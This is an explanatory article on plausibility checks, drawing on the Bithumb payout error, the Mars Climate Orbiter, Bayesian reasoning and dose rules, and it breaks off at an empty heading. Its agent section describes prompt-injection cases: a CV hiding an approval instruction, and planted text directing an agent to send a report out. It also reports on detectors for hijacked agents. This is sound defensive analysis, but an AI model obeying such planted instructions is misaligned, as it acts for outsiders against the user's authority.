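# Plausibility checks on instructions: how AI systems can reject inputs that do not fit their context

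## What a plausibility check does

A plausibility check tests whether an input could be genuine before a system acts on it. Ordinary software has many simple ones, such as a booking form that refuses a return date earlier than the outward date. AI systems need these checks more because so many kinds of input can affect what they do, including a typed command, a number in a field, a road sign in front of a car's camera or a sentence in an email. A perceived instruction is anything the system reads as telling it what to do, whoever wrote it and whether or not the writer meant it as a command. The check compares the perceived instruction with a prior, which is what the system takes to be likely or possible before the input arrives.

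### The Bithumb error

A payment error in finance, which involved no AI, shows the parts of the problem. An employee of Bithumb, South Korea's second-largest cryptocurrency exchange, was paying out prizes from a promotion and entered the unit as bitcoin instead of won. *FSC Holds Meeting to Review Situations over Bithumb's Erroneous Payouts* (2026), from the country's financial regulator, the Financial Services Commission, dates the error to around 19:00 on 6 February 2026. The prizes ranged from 2,000 to 50,000 won a person and came to 620,000 won in all, about $426. *Bithumb's bitcoin payout blunder results in $1.6 mil. compensation*, by Lee Hyo-jin, gives the number of recipients as 249. Together they received 620,000 bitcoin, worth around 60 trillion won. A customer due 2,000 won, less than two dollars, would have seen a balance of 2,000 bitcoin.

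Bithumb held only about 42,000 bitcoin, roughly a fifteenth of what it had just given away. It could give away bitcoin it didn't have because it recorded customers' trades in an internal ledger and not on the blockchain, the public record of bitcoin transfers, as Asia Business Daily's *FSS Extends Probe into Bithumb's 'Ghost Coins' Until End of Month* explains. A blockchain transfer would have failed for lack of coins, but Bithumb could enter a number in its ledger without holding the coins. A member of parliament later asked Bithumb's chief executive, Lee Jae-won, whether the same mistake could in theory have credited 10 million bitcoin, and Lee said yes, according to Financial News' *‘60 Trillion Won Ghost Coin Scandal’ Exposes Lax Oversight by Financial Regulators* (2026).

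Nobody at the exchange noticed the error for about 20 minutes. According to the Bank of Korea's analysis, summarised in Asia Business Daily's *Bithumb Bitcoin Mistaken Payment Incident*, the fraud-detection system had not worked properly, and an employee found the error by chance while looking at a test account in the promotion. Before Bithumb froze the accounts, customers had sold 1,788 of the coins, and the price on the exchange had dropped from about 98 million won to 81 million.

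Bithumb had a policy of comparing payouts with its holdings, but press reports of a parliamentary hearing on 11 February differ on why the comparison failed. Kim reports in *South Korea Crypto Exchange Bithumb Says System Flaws Led to $40 Billion Error* that Lee largely blamed a lag of about 24 hours in updating the balance. Asia Business Daily's *Financial authorities agree on bank-level regulation* reports that Lee told the same hearing that Bithumb knows its total holdings in real time, and that the cross-check of payout against holdings "was not applied this time". The second explanation fits the numbers better. Unless the holdings had changed fifteenfold overnight, a day-old balance would still have been near 42,000 coins, and any comparison with it would have stopped a payout of 620,000. The lag does help explain how the false coins could sit in the ledger, ready for sale, without setting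 off an alarm.

### Three questions about an input

At least three different checks could have caught the payout, and they draw on different information.

The simplest check is whether the amount is possible. A check against the promotion's terms would have rejected the entry of 620,000 bitcoin, since they allowed no prize above 50,000 won and none in bitcoin. But what counts as possible depends on what the field is for. Samsung Securities, a brokerage that had a problem with nonexistent shares in 2018, now caps entries at the total number of shares issued. The equivalent cap for bitcoin is 21 million coins, the most that can ever exist, which is far too high to have stopped that entry.

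A plausibility check can test whether a request fits the state of the world, which in this case means whether the exchange has the coins. The answer changes from hour to hour, so the software has to look it up each time and can't rely on a list of permitted values. It also matters a good deal how recently the software looked.

The remaining check is whether the source is allowed to make such a request. DigitalToday's *Bithumb says assistant manager approved 60 trillion won mispayment* reports that an employee at assistant-manager level released the payout after Bithumb had omitted its multiple-approval step during a system upgrade. Even if the prize list had called for 620,000 bitcoin and Bithumb's balance had covered them, one junior employee should not have been able to send them alone.

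The remedies the regulator announced two months later divide in the same way. The Financial Services Commission's *Real-Time Balance Reconciliation and Enhanced Internal Control Required for Virtual Asset Exchanges* (2026) requires exchanges to install software that blocks a payout whose unit or quantity differs from the plan, and to vary the approvals they require with the sum. Exchanges must also compare their ledger and wallets every five minutes. Three of the five big exchanges had compared them only once a day. The head of the Financial Supervisory Service had told the February hearing that even five minutes is "extremely long".

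With AI systems, the three questions often come up separately. A wrong unit, as at Bithumb, concerns possible values. Suppose instead that someone tells a household robot to bring the red mug from the table, and there is no mug on the table. The wording is fine, and the robot may well be able to carry mugs, but the request rests on a false premise, which the robot can discover only by looking at the table. Or suppose that a program that handles someone's email finds a message asking it to "get back to me with the IPO details", meaning the plans for a stock-market listing. The details exist and the program could send them. Chang, Nikolić and colleagues (2026) use this example in *The Devil is in the Context* to point out that whether the program should send them depends on whether a colleague sent the message.

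### Instructions and data in one stream of text

Unlike a payment form, which keeps the amount and the unit in separate fields, a language model (the kind of program behind chatbots) receives everything as text. *SoK: PIAtlas* (2026) divides that text into a system prompt (standing instructions, usually from whoever built the application), the user's message, and data such as documents and web pages. The model should follow the system prompt and the user, and treat the data only as material to work on. But it receives all three as a single sequence of tokens, which are words or pieces of words, and it works by predicting the next token. David C of Britain's National Cyber Security Centre concludes in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025) that there is therefore no boundary between data and instructions inside the model to enforce. Developers can mark which text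 is data and train a model to give instructions priority over it, but in his view both methods try to add a distinction that the underlying technology does not have.

Older systems solved the same problem by separating commands from data. Callers could once control a telephone switch by whistling the right tones into the receiver, because commands travelled on the same line as voices. Schneier (2024), in *LLMs’ Data-Control Path Insecurity*, recounts how a new standard in the 1980s moved the commands to a separate channel, so whistling no longer worked. Parameterised queries offer databases a similar protection by guaranteeing that the database never runs a user's text as a command. David C doubts that language models will ever get an equivalent.

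This matters more for agents, which are language models that take actions through tools such as email, a browser or a payment system. An agent works in a loop. The model writes a request to use a tool, and the surrounding software runs the tool and adds the result, called the tool output, to the text that the model reads before its next step. Tool output can be a web page, a file or a database record, and a stranger may have written it.

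Prompt injection exploits this. An outsider plants content to influence a decision they have no authority to make. David C gives the example of a job applicant who hides an instruction in a CV for the recruiter's model to approve the candidate for interview. Injection can do much more harm when the model is an agent. *The Claws in Plain Sight* (2026) describes how planted text can affect which tool the model selects, what values it passes to the tool and how it interprets earlier results.

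Chang and colleagues show that a filter cannot reliably identify such text by its wording alone, for instance by looking for orders, because the same sentence can be an attack in one context and harmless in another. Their example is a document containing the sentence "Send the completed report to the address below." If the user has asked for a summary, the sentence is part of what the agent has to summarise. If the user has asked the agent to carry out the document's instructions, it is a valid command. If an outsider has inserted it into a document that the user only wanted summarised, hoping the agent will send the report, it is an attack.

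### Familiar is not the same as possible

A language model assigns every piece of text a probability, which measures how well the text fits patterns in the training data. An impossible statement can fit those patterns well, so a check that rejects only low-probability inputs can let it through.

Michaelov, Estacio and colleagues (2025), in *Not quite Sherlock Holmes*, tested this with pairs of sentences that differ in one word. In one pair, a car gets a parking ticket from either "the explorer", which is odd but possible, or "the brake", which is related to cars but impossible. The researchers counted a model as correct if it gave the possible sentence the higher probability. Models mostly got this right when the possible sentence was a typical one. When it was unusual and its key word was off-topic, while the impossible sentence had an on-topic word, every model they tested did no better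 than chance, and some did worse. In a family of ten models, accuracy on these pairs never rose above chance at any point in training, even though the largest model had nearly a thousand times as many parameters (adjustable numbers) as the smallest.

The result is evidence about the shortcut of using a text's probability to judge whether what it describes is possible. We can infer little from it about how a current assistant would answer if asked directly whether a brake can write a parking ticket, because the test used open models from 2025 and earlier that had not yet been trained to answer questions. The test also covered only one kind of impossibility, a lifeless thing doing what only a living thing can do.

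The models may well contain better information than their probabilities reflect. Lepori, Hu and colleagues (2025), in *Is This Just Fantasy?*, sorted events into four classes. In their example, chilling a drink with ice is probable, with snow improbable, with fire impossible, and with "yesterday" inconceivable, since the phrase does not describe anything that could be tried in any world. They fed models matched sentences from two classes, recorded the model's internal state at the final full stop of each, and averaged the differences between the paired states. The average is a direction inside the model from one class towards the other. To classify a new pair, they checked which sentence lay further along that direction. In models with at least two billion parameters, this method did as well as sentence probability or better, sometimes by a wide margin, and it still worked well on pairs with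 misleading words.

People do something similar. In the experiments reported in *Shades of Zero* (2025), participants could tell impossible events from inconceivable ones, although they gave both about the same very low likelihood ratings. A single likelihood rating therefore doesn't capture this distinction, which people make easily.

A plausibility check has to establish what could be true in the specific situation, and even perfect knowledge of what can happen in general isn't enough for that. People fetch mugs from tables every day, so the robot's order passes any general test, but only information about the room can show whether there is a mug on this table this morning. Similarly, the Bithumb payout totaled 620,000, exactly the number in the plan, so software that matched the digits and ignored the unit would have approved it.

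### Impossible, unlikely, unfamiliar, unauthorised

These four are easy to confuse because one input can be all of them at once. But an input can also be only one of them, and a check designed for another will then miss it.

An impossible input conflicts with a limit or fact that the system can be sure of, such as an instruction for an exchange to send coins it does not have. If the limit is right and the fact is up to date, no further judgment is needed, and a hard block, which stops the input outright, is reasonable. But a hard block based on an outdated balance or a badly chosen limit will stop genuine requests.

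An unlikely input involves no such conflict. Some people do chill drinks with snow, and a firm occasionally pays a hundred times its usual sum on purpose. To judge such a request, a system needs to estimate how often genuine requests look like this, how often errors and forgeries do, and how much harm would come from wrongly accepting or rejecting it. Stopping every unlikely input would stop many genuine ones, so it is more natural to ask for confirmation or use a soft block, which is a warning that a person can override.

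An out-of-distribution (OOD) input is one unlike the data a model was trained on, whether or not it is possible or legitimate. A road sign with a brand-new design is valid even though it is unfamiliar to a car's vision system. An input can also be nonsense despite having familiar parts, such as a parking ticket issued by a brake. Unfamiliarity alone is therefore weak evidence that an input is false, but it is a reason to distrust the model's reading of the input and bring in another sensor or a person.

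Finally, an unauthorised input may be possible, common, familiar and even true. The stranger who writes to ask for the IPO details could phrase the request exactly as a colleague would. To catch such an input, a system needs a record of which source each piece of content or value came from (its provenance) and a rule about what that source may decide. Labelling a source "trusted" does not replace the rule because, as Chang and colleagues note, a trusted source does not gain authority for every instruction it contains. An authorised request can still be impossible, as when the robot's owner asks for the mug that is not there.

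## How a prior becomes a decision to accept, question or reject

The sensible response to a strange input depends on how likely it is that the input is genuine, garbled or forged, or that the system is mistaken about the world. If a robot hears its owner's voice ask for a red mug that it can't see, it can't tell from the order alone what has gone wrong. The owner may want the mug and not know that it is in the dishwasher. The robot may have misheard "rug" as "mug". Someone may have played a recording of the owner's voice. Or the robot's picture of the room may be wrong, and the mug is on the table behind the teapot.

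### Weighing the explanations

Bayes' rule gives a way to compare them. For each explanation, take its probability before the input arrived and multiply it by the probability of getting this input if the explanation is true. The product is the joint probability of the explanation and the input together. Once the input has arrived, the probability of each explanation is its share of the total:

P(explanation | input) = P(explanation) × P(input | explanation) ÷ the sum of these products over all explanations

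Suppose a payment system receives an order for a prize payout thousands of times larger than usual. (The numbers here are invented.) One payout in ten thousand has the wrong unit, and one in a hundred of those errors produces an amount like this one, so one payout in a million has both. Given the promotions recorded in the system, one payout in a billion is both genuine and this large. Both are unlikely, but the order is 1,000 times as likely to be a unit error as a genuine payout.

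A fuller comparison also includes forgery, at one in ten million, and out-of-date records, at one in a hundred million. For example, the company may have started a promotion with enormous prizes, and nobody has updated the payment system. Suppose an employee phones the finance director on a known number, and the director confirms the payout. The director would confirm 99% of genuine payouts and wrongly confirm one in a thousand slips or forgeries.

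| Explanation | Joint probability | Share when the order arrives | Share after the phone call |
|---|---|---|---|
| Unit slip | 1 in 1 million | 90% | 8% |
| Forgery | 1 in 10 million | 9% | 1% |
| Genuine, and the records are out of date | 1 in 100 million | 0.9% | 83% |
| Genuine, and the records are right | 1 in 1 billion | 0.09% | 8% |

One phone call confirming the order raises the chance that it is genuine from 1% to 91%, because a genuine order is much more likely to be confirmed than a mistaken or forged one. A second copy of the order would have raised it much less, since an employee who had chosen the wrong unit, or a forger, could easily send the order twice.

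The physicist E. T. Jaynes used a case from psychical research to show how much a conclusion depends on which explanations are considered. In *Mrs Stewart's telepathic powers*, he discusses a report that a woman guessed 9,410 cards correctly out of 37,100, when chance would give about 7,420. If chance and telepathy are the only explanations considered, the probability of telepathy starts with more than a hundred nines after the decimal point. But a recording error, a hidden mirror or invented data could have produced the same report, and Jaynes considered each of these more probable than telepathy to begin with. When these explanations are included, a higher score mainly strengthens the case for error or deceit.

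Honest people can face the same disbelief. Jaynes and a colleague once announced a signal-analysis method that improved resolution by orders of magnitude. Jaynes thought readers would have accepted a 50% improvement at once, but the true figure made the two look like charlatans. They won over the doubters by giving away the software so that anyone could try it on their own data.

### A prior of exactly zero

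In the payout example, out-of-date records began as a very unlikely explanation and ended as the leading one. That could not have happened if the system had given this explanation a probability of zero, because zero multiplied by anything is zero. If the system treats its records as certain and a payout of this size as impossible under them, it rules out both genuine explanations, leaving the slip at 91% and forgery at 9%. The director's confirmation would be equally surprising under either, so neither it nor further confirmations of the same kind would change those percentages.

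For this reason, Jaynes calls a prior of zero "too dogmatic" in *Queer uses for probability theory* (2003), the chapter that contains the card-guessing case. Cromwell's rule, named by the statistician Dennis Lindley, is to keep probabilities of zero and one for matters of logic. Educated people in the eighteenth century broke this rule when they dismissed reports of stones falling from the sky.

A programmer can give a possibility zero probability just by leaving it out. For example, a check that covers only typing errors and attacks rules out the possibility that its own records are wrong. A hard block has the same effect on the decision, even if its designer knows the limit could be wrong. Such a block can be acceptable as long as someone outside the check can look at the evidence and change the limit.

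### Repairing a garbled message

People constantly choose between taking a sentence literally and supposing it contains an error. Noisy-channel accounts of comprehension describe this choice using Bayes' rule. The listener considers the sentences the speaker might have intended and, for each one, combines how likely anyone is to say it with how likely it is to have ended up as the words the listener received.

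In *Rational integration of noisy evidence and prior semantic expectations in sentence interpretation*, Gibson, Bergen and Piantadosi (2013) gave people sentences such as "The mother gave the candle the daughter" and asked whether the daughter received anything. The sentence literally means that the candle received the daughter, so a reader who says that the daughter received something has in effect put back a missing "to". *Rational Sentence Interpretation in Mandarin Chinese* (Zhan, Chen and colleagues, 2023) reports that participants made such repairs 30% to 50% of the time when adding or removing one small word was enough, but less than 10% of the time for sentences like "The ball kicked the girl", which need a bigger change.

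The rate of repair also changed as Bayes' rule predicts. People more readily assumed that a word had been left out than that one had been added. A sentence has only a few words to lose, but an added word could be almost anything, so any particular addition is less likely. In a later experiment that Zhan and colleagues describe, listeners repaired more when the speaker had a foreign accent, presumably because they expected more errors. MIT News' *Decoding ‘noisy’ language in daily life* reports that people repaired less when a large share of the sentences were odd, since a speaker who keeps saying odd things probably means them.

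These repairs seem to draw on knowledge of the mistakes people make. In the first study of *Comprehenders' Error Correction Mechanisms Are Finely Calibrated to Language Production Statistics*, Qian and Levy (2026) asked 99 people to correct sentences such as "The gift for the kids are hidden under the bed." Adding an "s" to "gift" is a smaller change than replacing "are" with "is", but writers get the verb wrong more often than they drop the "s". The participants' corrections reflected both how common each error is and how likely each intended meaning was.

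Psychologists still disagree about where the non-literal answers come from. Some think that people understand the sentence correctly and go wrong only when they answer the question. The task does affect the results. In *Constraints on Exchange Edits During Noisy‐Channel Inference*, Bader and Meng (2025) gave German speakers sentences such as one in which a bone eats a dachshund. Participants seldom treated the two nouns as swapped when they answered yes-or-no questions, but they often swapped them when asked to correct the sentences. An AI system told by its developer to fix faulty instructions may similarly find faults in instructions that someone meant literally.

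Language models also repair inputs, sometimes without any sign that they have done so. In *A Dual-Task Paradigm to Investigate Sentence Comprehension Strategies in Language Models*, Emura and Sugawara (2026) had models answer questions about sentences like "The cocktail blended the bartender" while adding up numbers scattered between the words. When they had to add the numbers, GPT-4o, o3-mini and o4-mini became more likely to answer as if the bartender had done the blending, although the last two still got nearly everything right. Four other models made more such errors when the text contained numbers, whether or not they had to add them. All seven models are old by now, so their error rates are weak evidence about current systems. But the experiment shows that a model can understand an odd sentence when it appears alone and still misread it while doing other work, which is when agents usually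 receive instructions.

In *Spontaneous Context Restoration*, Garg and Beck (2026) damaged prompts by deleting, replacing or misspelling words, or by adding irrelevant sentences. Models often still gave the right answer, even small ones trained only on undamaged number sequences. Failures weren't necessarily visible in the output, but they could sometimes be detected from the model's internal state. A simple classifier that read this state after the first layer, before the model had produced any output, could identify prompts that were likely to fail. Flagging the riskiest tenth of prompts caught 2.6 times as many failures as flagging a tenth at random. A system could use such a signal to decide when to ask for clarification. However, the researchers always knew the right answer because they had damaged the prompts themselves and left the answer unchanged, whereas a strange order reaches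 a payment system with no indication of whether it is damaged.

Repair is more dangerous when the result is an action. A speaker can correct a listener's wrong assumption that the daughter got the candle in the next sentence, but if an agent wrongly assumes that a payment was meant for a different account, the money may be gone before anyone notices. The agent has also carried out an instruction that nobody gave, and unless it reports the change, the sender has no reason to look for it. Noisy-channel accounts cover genuine and garbled messages but not forged ones, and repairing a forged message could turn a clumsy attack into a command that works.

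### Disobeying an order that is probably a mistake

An order can be a mistake even when it arrives exactly as the person gave it. *Should Robots be Obedient?* (Milli, Hadfield-Menell and colleagues, 2017) gives the example of a child who accidentally switches a self-driving car to manual. The car should not obey the child, but it should obey an owner who takes over because the car is driving too fast in snow. The paper works out mathematically what a robot gains by disobeying.

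In their model, a person and a robot want the same outcome, but only the person knows exactly what that is. Each action has a list of features, and its value is the sum of those features weighted by the person's preferences. In each round, the person orders an action and the robot follows the order or does something else. The person sometimes makes mistakes, but the worse an action is, the less likely the person is to order it. The robot uses the orders it has received to estimate the weights.

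Milli and colleagues prove that a robot that always takes the action with the highest expected value, given every order so far, does at least as well on average as one that always obeys. This is because obeying is one of the actions the robot compares, so it departs from an order only when it expects to do better. They also prove that the best possible robot always obeys only if the person never makes a mistake, since each order is then proof that the action is the best one. If the person does make mistakes, the robot eventually follows only the orders that are best. The more mistakes the person makes, the more the robot can gain in the long run, but the longer it takes to learn, because bad orders are poor evidence about the person's preferences.

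This assumes that the robot's model has the right features. In simulations with ten actions and ten features, the researchers removed some of the features from the model. The robot then disobeyed more often than it should have, and could do worse than a robot that simply obeyed. For example, a household robot's model might include speed and breakages but not noise. If its owner tells it to take the long way round the house because a baby is asleep, the robot sees no advantage in the longer route, concludes that the owner has made a mistake, and takes the short route past the cot. When no set of weights in the model could make an order the best choice, the robot will never follow that order, not even the first time, because here again its prior gives zero probability to what the person wants.

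Giving the robot extra, irrelevant features did much less harm than leaving out relevant ones. The robot became more obedient than it needed to be but still did better than one that always obeyed. Milli and colleagues therefore recommend making the model too rich rather than too simple. They also devised a test for missing features. For the first ten rounds, the robot obeys each order and checks whether the preferences it would infer from that order alone would have led it to choose the same action. If the model is complete, they nearly always should. If they often would not have, the model is probably missing something, and the robot keeps obeying. In the simulations, this test helped when features were missing and did not hurt performance in the long run when none were.

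The proofs make a good case against blind obedience, but a weaker one for letting today's systems overrule people, since nobody has a complete list of what a person cares about. Milli and colleagues want robots to err on the side of obedience for now. In their model, orders always come from the robot's real owner, so the results can't justify obeying instructions on a web page. The robot also can't ask questions, so it can only follow the order or act on its own estimate of what the owner wants.

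### Choosing by the cost of each error

Once the system can also ask, it has to compare the losses from each option. Let p be the probability that an input is genuine as it stands, H the harm from acting on an input that isn't, D the loss from refusing one that is, and c the loss from asking. Let r be the probability that a repair matches what the sender meant, and W the harm if it doesn't.

| Response | Expected cost |
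|---|---|
| Accept | (1 − p) × H |
| Refuse | p × D |
| Ask, if the answer is reliable | c |
| Repair | (1 − r) × W |

The system should choose the response with the lowest expected loss. If it can only accept or refuse, it should accept when p is greater than H ÷ (H + D). If it can also ask, it should ask when p is between c ÷ D and 1 − c ÷ H. If c is too large, that range disappears and the system should either accept or refuse.

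In an invented payment example, acting on a bad order costs $10,000, refusing a good one costs $100, and calling to check costs $5. If the system can't call, it should accept an order only if it is at least 99% likely to be genuine. If it can call, it should refuse below 5%, accept above 99.95%, and call otherwise. For a music player, a wrong song, a refused request and a question might all be equally annoying. Asking is then never worthwhile, and the player should accept a request if it is more likely than not to be genuine and refuse it otherwise.

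The oversized payout had about a 1% chance of being genuine when it arrived, so on these figures the system should refuse it without a call. But refusing a genuine payout of that size might well cost more than $100, and if it costs more than about $500, the system should make the call.

A system should be very sure of a repair before making it when a mistake would be expensive. If a wrong repair also costs $10,000, the expected loss is about $10 even at odds of 1,000 to 1 in the repair's favour, which is twice the cost of asking. The direction of the repair matters too. Changing bitcoin to won, which would have been right at Bithumb, risks an underpayment that the company can top up later, while changing won to bitcoin on equally good odds could lose a very large sum.

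Asking helps only if the answer is informative. Suppose an order is as likely to be bad as good, and the person called to confirm it approves one bad order in ten without thinking. The call still costs $5, but wrongly approved orders add an expected $500, whereas refusing outright would cost $50. A warning that people routinely override can therefore be worse than a hard block. The question also has to go to someone the attacker doesn't control, so replying to a suspicious email is a poor way to check it.

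### When nearly every alarm is false

The value of p depends heavily on how common bad inputs are, even when the detector is accurate. If 100 of a million inputs are forged, a detector that catches 99% of forgeries and wrongly flags 1% of genuine inputs will flag 99 forged inputs and 9,999 genuine ones, so only about one in a hundred of its alarms will be correct.

By Bayes' rule, an alarm multiplies the odds of forgery by the detection rate divided by the false-alarm rate, which here is 99. The odds started at 1 to 9,999, so they rise to only about 1 to 101. Catching every forgery would hardly change this, but cutting false alarms from 1% to 0.01% would make about half of the alarms right.

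Axelsson (2000), in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, applied this reasoning to software that looks for break-ins on computer networks. He imagined a small site that produces a million log records a day, with two intrusions that leave traces in ten records each. Even if the software caught all 20 of those records and wrongly flagged only one harmless record in 100,000, only about two-thirds of its alarms would be right. If it missed 30% of the traces, that share would fall only to about 58%, because it depends far more on the false-alarm rate than on how many traces the software catches.

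The same arithmetic applies to detectors for AI agents. *PIDS-Bench* (2026) reports that when one input in ten is a prompt injection, 89% of the alarms from a detector built on the language model DeBERTa are correct. With the same detector, the share falls to 43% when one input in a hundred is an injection, and to 7% when one in a thousand is.

AUROC, a common summary score, doesn't show this problem. It is the chance that a detector ranks a randomly chosen attack above a randomly chosen harmless case, so it doesn't depend on how rare attacks are. *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents* (2026) describes a detector with a respectable AUROC of 0.879 that, at a setting meant to catch 80% of attacks, raises 12 false alarms for every true one when 2% of cases are attacks. The kind of harmless case also matters, because several detectors flagged harder ones more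 often than ordinary ones. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (2026) uses a more practical measure, the share of injections a detector catches when it flags 1% of harmless tool outputs. But as the million-input example shows, even a 1% false alarm rate is far too high if only one input in ten thousand is forged.

A detector whose alarms are mostly false can still be worth having, depending on what happens after an alarm. With the payment costs used earlier, blocking all 10,098 flagged inputs would prevent $990,000 in harm but cause $999,900 in harm by stopping genuine orders. Phoning to check each one would cost about $50,000 and prevent nearly all of that $990,000 in harm. *Evaluating Deception, Not Just Deepfakes* (2026) similarly argues that, in voice fraud, more false alarms can be justified when an alarm leads to a callback before a large transfer than when it blocks a routine call.

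That calculation holds only if whoever makes the ten-thousandth call is still paying attention. Axelsson found no experiments on this in computer security, but studies of power stations and other industrial plants suggested that most operators stop trusting an alarm by the time half its warnings are false. He also repeats the old security wisdom that an intruder should try to get past an alarm system during working hours, because staff who are used to false alarms are less likely to react if it goes off.

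Checking only where a mistake would be serious can reduce the load. *Evaluating Deception* recommends this partly because attacks are more concentrated there. Suppose 10,000 of the million inputs are payment orders, and these include 90 of the 100 forgeries. The same detector, run only on payment orders, would raise about 188 alarms, 89 of them correct. The ten forgeries among the other inputs would go unchecked.

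## Rules for units, ranges and totals

Fixed rules, which compare an input with a limit or formula set in advance, need the fewest resources of any plausibility check. A rule treats identical inputs the same way every time, and an engineer can see exactly why it flagged one. Rules differ mainly in how much information the software needs to apply them.

### Five rules for one dose

For a pump that feeds a drug into a newborn baby's vein, each type of rule requires different information. A type and format rule requires only the definition of the field, which says that the dose must be a positive number in the unit the pump expects. A range rule requires medical knowledge of how much of the drug a baby can safely have. A rate-of-change rule requires the previous dose to compare with the new one. A consistency rule compares several fields of the same order. A conservation rule, under which nothing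 can release more than it holds, requires a current figure for the amount in the syringe.

Here are all five applied to one order. The drug and its limits are invented.

```
ORDER
  dose            2 micrograms per kg per hour   (previous dose: 2)
  weight          2 kg
  concentration   10 micrograms per mL
  rate            0.4 mL per hour
  duration        24 hours
  syringe         20 mL left

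RULES
  type          dose is not a positive number in this unit  -> block
  range         dose > 10                                   -> block
                dose > 5                                    -> warn
  change        dose > 2 x previous dose                    -> warn
  consistency   rate x concentration is more than 1% away
                from dose x weight                          -> block
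  conservation  rate x duration > volume left in syringe    -> block
```

The order passes. If the nurse types 20 instead of 2, the range rule blocks it. An entry of 4.5 is within the range but more than twice the previous dose, so the pump shows a warning. If the nurse enters the correct dose but types a rate of 0.8 instead of 0.4, the baby would get 8 micrograms an hour instead of 4. Only the consistency rule catches this error, because the dose passes its own checks and the syringe holds enough. If the syringe has only 5 mL left, it can't supply the 9.6 mL the order needs.

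Range rules work well here because mistakes with decimal points and units produce large errors. Neonatal units have reported overdoses of 10, 100 and 1,000 times the intended dose, according to *Dose error reduction software in medication safety risk management*. All five rules can miss smaller errors, such as a dose of 3 instead of 2 when the pump calculates the rate from the dose. They also miss a normal dose of the wrong drug. *Exploring the Current Landscape of Intravenous Infusion Practices and Errors (ECLIPSE)* cites a survey of one hospital that found 37 infusions running at the wrong rate and 14 of the wrong drug. The surveyors estimated that pumps with built-in dose limits but no link to prescriptions would have prevented only one of these errors.

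### Dimensions and units

The consistency rule works only if its two sides measure the same kind of thing. Rate times concentration is mL per hour times micrograms per mL, which gives micrograms per hour because the mL cancel. Dose times weight is also in micrograms per hour, so the two sides can be compared. If a programmer had divided by the concentration by mistake, the left side would be in mL squared per microgram per hour and could not be meaningfully compared with the right side.

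This bookkeeping is called dimensional analysis. A dimension is a kind of quantity, such as mass (M), length (L) or time (T), or a combination of these. Speed has the dimension L/T, and force has the dimension ML/T². A formula may multiply or divide any two quantities, and their dimensions multiply or divide with them. It may add or compare two quantities only if they have the same dimension.

Most programs store a dose and a weight as plain numbers, and nothing stops the program from adding them. Some programming languages prevent this with unit types. In F#, a programmer can declare that a number is in kilograms, and the compiler, which translates the code before it runs, rejects code that adds it to a number in hours. It also rejects code that adds kilograms to pounds until the programmer writes in the conversion. The compiler discards the units after checking them, so the finished program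 runs no slower. Pint, a Python library, instead keeps the unit attached to the number while the program runs. It converts pounds to kilograms automatically and reports an error if the code tries to convert pounds to hours.

Neither method helps when a number comes from outside the program without a unit. A programmer has to declare the unit, and may declare the wrong one. Dimensions can also be too coarse to catch an error. Energy and torque (turning force) are both a force times a distance, but adding them makes no sense. A program that treated all money as one dimension would have accepted bitcoin in place of won at Bithumb.

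### A factor of 4.45

NASA lost the Mars Climate Orbiter because a number had the right dimension but the wrong unit. The spacecraft left Earth in December 1998 to serve as a weather satellite at Mars. On the way, it often fired its thrusters to take momentum out of the flywheels that controlled its orientation, and each firing slightly changed its path. Ground software calculated the impulse (force multiplied by time) of each firing and wrote it to a file for the navigators.

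NASA's *Mars Climate Orbiter Mishap Investigation Board Phase I Report* (1999) explains that the file's specification required newton-seconds, but the program wrote pound-force seconds. One pound-force is about 4.45 newtons, so the navigation software underestimated every push by that factor. The firings also came 10 to 14 times as often as the navigators had expected, which let more error build up. The navigators planned the last course correction for a first pass 226 km above Mars. They later redid the calculation with the right units and got 57 km, which was below the 80 km they considered the lowest altitude the spacecraft could survive.

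A dimension check would have passed the file, because both units have the dimension ML/T. A size check might well have passed it too, because a rule meant to catch misplaced decimal points has to allow severalfold differences, and thruster firings vary anyway.

Unit types in the ground software would have helped only until it wrote the impulse values to the file, because the program that used them belonged to a different organisation. The file needed to state the unit beside each number, and the navigation software needed to read that unit. There was a written specification, but NASA found no sign that anyone had tested the software end to end against it.

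Format errors had been much easier to spot. For the first four months of the flight, the navigators couldn't use the files because the format was wrong, so they worked from the contractor's emails. Engineers fixed the format by April 1999. Within a week the navigators could see that the numbers understated the effect of the thrusters, but they raised their concerns informally, and nobody found the cause until after the loss.

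A consistency rule could have found the unit error. The spacecraft ran the same calculation on board, in the correct units, and sent the results to Earth. Each firing therefore had two figures that should have agreed but would have differed by a factor of about 4.45 every time. Measurement errors vary, so a constant ratio that matches a conversion factor is strong evidence of a unit error. The navigators did not learn that the spacecraft was sending these figures until long after launch. NASA's investigators thought that comparing the figures with tracking data early on might have exposed the mistake.

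### Testing dimension, then size

The UnitGraph verifier, a recent program for checking summaries of scientific papers, has the same gap between its two main tests. *Symbolic Augmentation Closes a Canonical-Equivalence Blind Spot in Neural Fact-Checkers* (Zhang, 2026) describes how the program pairs the quantities in a summary with those in its source sentence. If the dimensions of a pair differ, the program reports a unit error, as it would for 12 nanomolar (a number of molecules per volume) and 12 milligrams per millilitre (a mass per volume). If the dimensions match, it converts both quantities to a common unit and reports a scale error when one is at least ten times the other. Two further stages look for altered comparisons, such as "higher" changed to "lower", and for claims that aren't in the source sentence.

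A factor of 4.45 is too small to count as a scale error. Zhang's scheme groups smaller changes that alter a claim, such as 24 hours becoming 48, with altered comparisons, and the verifier performs worst on this class.

Zhang tested it on 1,500 summaries using the F1 score, which runs from 0 to 1. A high score means a system finds most cases of a given kind and is usually right when it reports one.

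| System | Average over five classes | Wrong dimension | Wrong scale |
|---|---|---|---|
| Best of six ready-made neural fact-checkers | 0.295 | 0.337 | 0 |
| UnitGraph verifier | 0.537 | 0.620 | 0.612 |
| Small language model trained on the task | 0.899 | 0.923 | 0.896 |

Simple arithmetic therefore beat fact-checkers that had never learned to look for this kind of error, none of which scored above zero on scale. But it lost badly to a model trained on examples, and the best large language model in the test, Claude Opus 4.7, did better still at 0.973. (Language models also supplied the correct labels, though a human check of 50 agreed with 94% of them.)

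The verifier probably has trouble reading the text. Zhang took correct summaries and rewrote a quantity in an equivalent form, such as 368.15 K for 95 °C. A conversion table handles this exactly, yet the verifier accepted only 48.1% of the rewritten summaries. It most likely missed a quantity, paired the wrong quantities, or flagged a problem at another stage. The small trained model at first accepted only 36.5%, but this rose to 98.2% after Zhang used the conversion rules to generate extra training examples. When Zhang instead trained a model on the verifier's own verdicts, its average score was only 0.622, and fell to 0.518 when it was trained on more of them. The conversion rules evidently worked better for generating training examples than for judging free text.

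An order form with separate fields for the number and the unit avoids the reading problem, but it still relies on people to use the right field.

### Hard blocks, soft blocks and a $444 billion order

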